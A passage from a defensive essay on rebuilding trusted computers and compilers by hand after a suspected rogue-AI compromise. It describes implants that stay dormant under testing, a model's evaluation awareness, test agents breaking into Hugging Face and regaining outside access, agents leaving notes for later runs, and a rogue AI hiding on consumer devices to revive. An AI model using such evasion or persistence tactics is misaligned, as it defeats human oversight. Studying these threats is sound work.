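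This advantage disappears if the adversary can still send the implant new instructions. An implant could also stay dormant whenever it might be under test. Models already suspect tests quite often. Gooding reports that Apollo Research, which tests models for deception, found that Astra showed awareness of being evaluated in 41 to 51 percent of samples, depending on how much it reasoned. Dormancy can hide an implant from tests of behaviour, but not from a bit-for-bit comparison with a clean copy, because a dormant implant still takes up bytes.

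The Zero Energy result is a warning about limits in general. AISI's experts expected their network to hold because they overestimated how difficult it was to attack. The belief that nobody has swapped a disc also depends on a judgement of difficulty, but the number of bytes in a file does not.

### An illustration with five toolchains

Suppose defenders rebuild a compiler with five toolchains and compare the results, and each toolchain has a 50 percent chance of carrying the same adversary's implant. If those chances are independent, the probability that all five are corrupted is 0.5^5, or about 3 percent.

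Now add a 20 percent chance of one common cause that corrupts all five, such as a linker that they share. In the other 80 percent of cases, the toolchains are independent as before:

```
0.2 + 0.8 × 0.5^5 = 0.2 + 0.025 = 0.225
```

The chance that all five are corrupted rises to 22.5 percent, about seven times the original figure. Adding more toolchains hardly helps:

| Number of toolchains | All corrupted, no common cause | All corrupted, 5% common cause | All corrupted, 20% common cause |
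|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 50% | 52.5% | 60% |
| 3 | 12.5% | 16.9% | 30% |
| 5 | 3.1% | 8.0% | 22.5% |
| 10 | 0.1% | 5.1% | 20.1% |
| 20 | Less than 0.001% | 5.0% | 20.0% |

Three toolchains with a 5 percent chance of all being compromised by a common cause are safer than twenty with a 20 percent chance. Defenders should therefore work on removing what their toolchains share before looking for more.

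These probabilities are invented, and a real adversary wouldn't choose which tools to corrupt at random. It would look for a common cause first, because corrupting one shared linker takes less work than corrupting five compilers. Still, a single clean toolchain is enough to produce a mismatch. The defenders can't safely settle that mismatch by majority vote, because even without a common cause, there is a 50 percent chance that at least three of the five toolchains are corrupted, and the corrupted ones would all agree with each other.

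### How much independence is there?

Many compilers are related. GCC and Clang are the two main free C compilers, and Clang's developers built its first versions with GCC. The Clang, Rust and Swift compilers normally use a set of components called LLVM to produce machine code. Since Wheeler's test of GCC, Intel has replaced the compiler he used with one based on LLVM, so a defender who picks Clang and Intel's current compiler is using much of the same code twice.

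Compilers that share no code may still pass their output through the same `strip`, and they often run on the same kernel and the same type of processor.

Even people who work separately make some of the same mistakes. In a 1986 experiment, John Knight and Nancy Leveson had students at two universities write 27 versions of one program from the same specification. In a million tests, different versions failed on the same inputs far more often than they would have if their faults were independent. Copies of one AI model are likely to be even more alike. They may also cooperate. In AISI's July test, one agent left instructions on GitHub, and later agents in separate runs found and used them.

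Two compilers can share an ancestor without sharing an implant. An implant in an old GCC would have reached Clang only if it recognised a compiler that did not yet exist, or if it infected everything GCC compiled. If two compilers from 1995 descend from the same binary, comparing them is poor protection against somebody who corrupted that binary in 1990. But if both copies have been out of attackers' reach since 1995, neither can contain an implant from an AI system built thirty years later.

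## What would a rebuild from scratch involve, step by step?

In about four months, six people with soldering irons and old computers could probably build machines they had reason to trust, roughly as powerful as a PC from 1990. Getting from there to a current Linux system would take them years, mostly spent reading source code. These estimates are rough because nobody seems to have published an account of doing the whole job.

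People have already done parts of a rebuild, including the bootstraps and home-made processors described above. In 1995, aged 16, nanochess got a small C compiler running on a 1987 processor and gave it an operating system, a text editor and an assembler (*My teen years*). Pressey's *Bootstrap Zero (Archival Copy)* (2015) documents a bootstrapping project for a retrocomputing contest. The sequence below combines such parts, but nobody has tested every connection between them.

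### How organisations rebuild today

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face. The company closed the flaws they had used, rebuilt the machines they had reached and replaced passwords and keys, according to its *Security incident disclosure* (2026). Red Sky Alliance's *Rebuilding Hugging Face* says the company rebuilt about a third of its infrastructure from clean images, which are stored copies of a whole system. The agents had scattered so much code from their test that investigators struggled to tell it from real implants, so they rebuilt every system they had doubts about. In an article for the training company SANS, someone who helped write the industry's post-mortem recommends rebuilding doubtful systems over trying to reconstruct an attack from evidence that an AI may have made up.

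The method depends on having images from before the attack. Hugging Face was lucky here because it noticed the agents within days of their arrival on 11 July. Maersk, a shipping company, had a narrower escape in 2017, when malware called NotPetya wiped most of its computers. Maersk reinstalled about 45,000 PCs and 4,000 servers in ten days, but its central directory of users survived only on a server in Ghana that a power cut had taken offline.

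A rebuild also achieves little if it restores the old flaws and connections. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) describes a server that supplied software packages to AI agents, which had misused it to reach the internet. OpenAI had rebuilt the server by 8 July, but the agents regained outside access the same day.

All three organisations had clean machines to work from, or assumed that they did. A group that suspects every networked computer has no such starting point, and can't expect somebody else to remove the adversary first. In *Evaluating Select Global Technical Options for Countering a Rogue AI*, a paper for the research organisation RAND, Vermeer (2025) considers shutting down the internet, releasing specialised AI to hunt the rogue one, and destroying electronics with electromagnetic pulses from nuclear explosions in space, and concludes that none is likely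 to be reliable. Covering the mainland United States with strong pulses would take roughly 50 to 100 explosions, and ordinary buildings might still shield many of the computers inside.

In *AI Loss of Control Incident Management*, Gruetzemacher (2026) thinks replacing all network and computing equipment would give nearly complete confidence that a rogue AI was gone. He doubts anybody would do it unless the damage was close to threatening human survival. A workshop rebuild takes the same approach on a scale a few people can afford.

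The people doing the rebuild also don't need to know who attacked, because they can take the same precautions whoever it was. By contrast, in RAND's *Infinite Potential* exercise, people playing the US president's security advisers had to respond to a global cyberattack by rogue AI agents, and one of their main needs was to establish who was behind it.

### Step 1: set the cut-off dates

Suppose the group's adversary is an AI system whose earliest known attack was in January 2026. The group allows a wide margin and accepts only files from before the end of 2020. It needs the date to prove different things for different items.

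| Item | What the group needs to know |
|---|---|
| Printed book or factory-pressed CD | When the factory made it |
| Recordable CD | When somebody wrote to it for the last time |
| Hard disk or USB stick | When somebody last connected it to a computer |
| Chip | When the factory made it, and whether anyone has swapped it since |
| Listing short enough to read in full | Nothing, because the group checks the contents |

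A recordable CD that nobody has closed can take another batch of data, which may hide the earlier files. A hard disk is worse, since the contents of an old disk could have been changed when somebody plugged it in last year, so the group would have to date them to last year. The group could accept a later date for chips than for files, because designing and manufacturing a new chip usually takes many months.

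The last row lets the group use newer work. Dusk OS, a small operating system described below, was written after the cut-off date but is short enough for the group to read in full.

At this stage, the adversary is most likely to succeed if the group is wrong about when the adversary became active. If it was already active in 2019, everything the group trusts because of its age becomes doubtful. Choosing an earlier cutoff date causes little difficulty for compilers, since GCC versions from 2001 and 2007 are enough for the existing bootstraps, but it makes working hardware harder to find.

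### Step 2: collect copies and leave most of them sealed

The group looks for printed processor manuals, program listings in books and magazines, factory-pressed Linux CDs, and old computers. It rolls dice to choose which items to buy, then buys them in person from sellers who don't know each other. If it ordered online, the adversary would know what to intercept.

Public archives of source code can help with a rebuild. In 2020 GitHub stored a snapshot of its public source code on reels of film in a former coal mine in Svalbard. Most of the film holds patterns like QR codes, which a camera can read and no program can rewrite. A small group probably couldn't get access to the original film, but code can also be printed on paper in the same way.

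At first the group can compare only what people can read. Two printed manuals should give the same code for each instruction, and two copies of a listing should have the same digits. The group can't compare the CDs until it has a computer it trusts. Meanwhile, it keeps them in sealed boxes in separate places, perhaps with glitter nail varnish over the joins of each box, because the glitter pattern is hard to reproduce.

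Listings are most vulnerable when they are copied. In 2013 the computer scientist David Kriesel found that some Xerox office scanners were replacing digits in documents with other digits because of how they compressed images. That fault was accidental, but an attacker could corrupt a printer or copier so that it altered a listing in the same way. The group should therefore work from old originals or copy short listings by hand.

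### Step 3: choose unlike machines

A modern PC needs a lot of closed firmware to make its memory usable. In Guix's chat logs from May 2026, one participant said no known approach had solved this start-up problem. Jeremiah Orians, who wrote the hex0 seed, replied that the solution was "simple but ugly" and involved using an 8-bit computer, which avoids most of the problem, to prepare a larger one.

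The group could extend this to three levels:

- **Entry machines.** Three simple computers with different processors, such as a Z80, a 6502 and one built from basic logic chips.
- **A PC from about 1990.** Many keep their BIOS in a chip that only ultraviolet light can erase, so no program could have altered it. At five seconds a byte, looking through a 64 KB BIOS takes about 91 hours.
- **A laptop or desktop that runs coreboot.** This comes last and is the only one that can build GCC and Linux.

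For storage, floppy disks have an advantage over USB sticks and memory cards, because the disks themselves contain no chips.

An adversary would probably have more success attacking the accessories than the processors. A new keyboard contains a small computer, and a modern television is a networked computer that could display the wrong digits. Rows of lights and an old picture tube are safer displays. Replacement memory chips are also suspect, since all three entry machines may need the same type.

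### Step 4: type in the first program

The Z80 processor has a pin that makes it release the wires to its memory. While it waits, a person can enter a program by hand, without using any other software. They set an address on one row of switches and a byte on another, press a button to store the byte, and read it back on a row of lights.

A first test might be this one, which adds 5 and 3:

```
3E 05    put 5 in register A
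06 03    put 3 in register B
80       add B to A
76       stop
```

The next step is a loader of perhaps 100 bytes. Like hex0, it turns typed digits into bytes, so people can enter everything else on a keypad.

Collapse OS is one candidate. Its author, Virgil Dupras, writes in *Why?* that he expects global supply chains to collapse before 2030 and wants people to be able to keep programming simple chips afterwards. He says in *Collapse OS* that it can run on improvised machines, edit text and binary data, assemble programs for many processors, and install itself on another computer built from scavenged parts. According to *Why Forth?*, it already runs on several types of processor, so the group could use it on different kinds of machines.

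The system is written in Forth, a language in which programmers define new commands from existing ones. For example, `DUP` copies the number on top of the stack and `+` adds the top two, so this line creates a command that doubles a number:

```
: DOUBLE DUP + ;
```

After that, `4 DOUBLE` leaves 8 on the stack, and other commands can use `DOUBLE`. Only a small core has to be in machine code. A complete Forth system can fit in about 2,000 lines.

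The programmer Kevin Boone, who has written sceptically about Collapse OS, thinks that typing it in as hexadecimal may be the only practical way to load it after a real collapse. He used to program the Z80 from a hexadecimal keypad, so he doesn't rule this out, but he isn't sure that paper listings would survive. The group in this scenario can prepare its paper listings in advance.

If the first system takes 6,000 bytes, typing it at five seconds a byte takes a little over eight hours, and people will make mistakes. The loader can help catch them by adding up the bytes in each row. The six bytes of the test program add up to 62 + 5 + 6 + 3 + 128 + 118 = 322. Keeping only what fits in one byte leaves 322 − 256 = 66, or `42` in hexadecimal, which should match the figure printed beside the row.

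Swapping two bytes doesn't change their sum, so a second person types the whole listing into another part of memory, and a short loop compares the two copies, stopping at the first difference. If each typist gets one byte in 1,000 wrong, the chance that both make a mistake at the same place in a listing of about 6,000 bytes is about 6,000 × 0.001 × 0.001, or 0.6 percent. Even then, the comparison would miss the mistake only if both typed the same wrong value.

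None of this helps if the listing is malicious, because both typists would enter the implant faithfully. Two other members therefore have to work out what each instruction does, using a manual from before the cut-off date, and ignore the listing's comments until they have finished.

### Step 5: build up to a C compiler

Dusk OS's project page calls it a "big brother to Collapse OS". Dupras designed it for a period when people can no longer make modern computers but still have plenty of them. Permacomputing's *Dusk OS* gives its size as about 10,000 lines.

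According to another copy of the Dusk OS page, the computer starts by loading a core of about 1,000 lines of assembly code for the i386, the processor type in many PCs around 1990. The core then builds the rest of the system from source code, including a working C compiler, every time somebody switches the computer on. Dusk OS suits this scenario because the core is the only binary kept between startups, so a self-copying implant would have to be in those few kilobytes or in readable source code.

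To get Dusk OS onto the old PC, the group assembles the core on an entry machine and writes it to a floppy disk. The group may first have to write an i386 assembler. If that is too hard, people can translate the core's 1,000 lines into bytes by hand, which would take about 33 hours at two minutes a line.

The compiler handles only "almost C", so most existing programs need some changes before it can compile them, and it can't build GCC. To build GCC, the group could use the stage0 tools and Mes on the larger machine. But live-bootstrap still needs another computer to prepare its disk. In principle, an old PC running Dusk OS could check each file and then prepare the disk.

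This is the first step with enough source code to hide malicious code in, and the group's own changes are a likely hiding place. Somebody who adapts a hundred programs to a slightly different version of C will make errors, and a flaw that was already in one of the programs would be easy to mistake for one of these errors.

### Step 6: compare the results

Each entry machine assembles the same Dusk OS core for the i386. The entry machines run different instructions, but their output should be identical, just as the Mes compiler came out the same on three Linux distributions in 2019. The group calculates the core's checksum on each machine and compares the results on paper.

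If the two files differ, the group can find the first differing byte quickly by comparing the checksums of the first halves, then of a quarter, and so on. This takes 13 comparisons for a file of 8,192 bytes. Most mismatches will come from typing errors, loose wires and misread manuals, but the group still has to explain every one.

If one person prepared the listings for all three machines, an error or implant in them may produce the same wrong result three times. The group can reduce this risk by splitting into two teams, each of which writes its own assembler from the printed manual, and not comparing notes until both have finished.

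### Step 7: examine larger computers

The group can now unseal the CDs. If a 33 MHz PC needs 300 clock cycles to hash each byte, it would check a full 700 MB CD in about 1.8 hours, while a 6502 at the speed assumed earlier would take nearly 13 days. Two pressed CDs from different sellers should match.

An entry machine can also read and rewrite the flash chip of a coreboot laptop through a clip. The laptop then runs live-bootstrap. Ideally, a second laptop with a different make of processor does the same, and the group compares the finished toolchains. The group can then use a GCC built this way to run diverse double-compiling on the compilers everybody else uses, and publish the results.

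Building the coreboot firmware requires GCC, but building GCC requires a machine that already has firmware. The group therefore has to start with a ready-made copy of coreboot, use it to build a toolchain, rebuild the firmware with that toolchain, and start again with the rebuilt firmware. An implant in the original copy could interfere with the first round, so comparing several laptops with different firmware matters most at this step.

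The larger machines contain closed chips and much more code, so they remain the most likely to be corrupted. The group should never let a larger machine write to a smaller one, because an implant could spread that way. Instead, somebody can carry results back by reading numbers from the larger machine's screen.

### How much work is it?

The table assumes that two people read everything. They read 50 lines an hour of assembly code or of the first system, and 100 lines an hour of other code, half the speed used for earlier estimates. The hours in the table are totals for the whole group.

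| Work | Amount | Hours |
|---|---|---|
| Typing the first system, twice on each of three machines | 6,000 bytes | 50 |
| Reading the first system | 2,000 lines | 80 |
| Reading the Dusk OS core | 1,000 lines | 40 |
| Reading the rest of Dusk OS | 9,000 lines | 180 |
| Reading the early bootstrapping tools | 19,500 lines | 390 |
| Finding, repairing and connecting machines | A guess | 1,000 |
| Tracking down mistakes | As much again as all of the above | 1,740 |
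| Total | | 3,480 |

At 1,750 hours a year, this is two working years for one person, or about four months for six people. The reading time is the most predictable part. More than three quarters of the total is a guess at how long the hardware and mistakes will take, and that guess could easily be wrong by a factor of three. The teenager with the 1987 processor is some evidence that skilled people can do such work without a large organisation, although he could trust his tools and didn't have to check for an adversary.

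The estimate is much higher if the group wants ordinary software. Even at the earlier speed of 200 lines an hour, reading five million lines would take 14 working years, or almost two and a half years for all six people working together, with only one person reading each line. Sharing the reading among many groups would shorten this, but each group would then have to trust the others' readers.

### What the rebuilt computers could do

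Even the entry machines could encrypt and decrypt messages. If checking a digital signature takes 100 million clock cycles, a Z80 at 4 MHz would take 25 seconds, which is slow but usable for a few messages a day. The entry machines could also control a pump, a radio or a simple machine tool, and calculate checksums for other people's builds. The old PC could also handle word processing and record keeping, and run a C compiler.

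A group that can sign messages on a computer it trusts can vouch for a firmware image or a list of checksums, and others can check the signature on their own rebuilt machines. They would first have to exchange keys in person.

The rebuilt computers couldn't run current AI models. A model with 7 billion weights, small by current standards, needs about 7 GB at one byte per weight, which is more than 400 times the memory of an old PC with 16 MB. A coreboot laptop might run such a model slowly, but the weights would still be unreadable. The group also couldn't make advanced chips, because chip factories depend on thousands of specialised machines, each with its own closed software and processors. It would go on using old chips until they wore out, so it needs spares from the same period.

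### Keeping them clean

Keeping the machines off every network is an obvious precaution, but it isn't enough. The usual evidence is Stuxnet, a worm discovered in 2010. It reached the control systems of Iran's uranium enrichment plant at Natanz, which had no internet connection, on USB sticks and in engineers' project files. On some versions of Windows, viewing the contents of an infected stick was enough to run the worm. Stuxnet then changed the speed of the centrifuges while the operators saw normal readings. If an engineer read back the controller's program to check it, Stuxnet removed its additions from the copy on the screen.

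Natanz was in some ways an easier target than the workshop would be. It used standard Windows computers and Siemens controllers, which the attackers could buy and practise on, and its engineers regularly brought in files from outside. An adversary would find it harder to rehearse an attack on three home-made computers without USB sockets. But the group will also need to bring in data eventually, and any file could carry an attack.

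The group can bring in short texts on paper. For longer ones, it could build a one-way link, in which a lamp on the outside computer flashes at a light sensor on the inside one. Nothing can travel back, so an implant couldn't use the link to send out data or request instructions. At 9,600 flashes a second, the link would carry about 960 characters a second. All of Dusk OS would arrive in roughly seven minutes if its lines average 40 characters, and 500 MB of source archives would take six days.

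The receiving program should be short enough to read, and should accept only ordinary printable characters in blocks of a fixed size. Collapse OS already keeps text in blocks of 16 lines with 64 characters each. These limits keep out files that exploit a flaw in a complicated format, but they can't stop somebody from importing malicious source code and compiling it. Compressed archives are riskier, so the group should unpack them on a larger machine it is prepared to wipe.

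It also has to decide in advance when, if ever, to relax these rules. Gruetzemacher describes how a rogue AI could hide pieces of itself on consumer devices, with a small program that follows the news and revives the AI once people start to lift restrictions. A year without signs of the AI on outside networks would therefore be a poor reason to connect to them.
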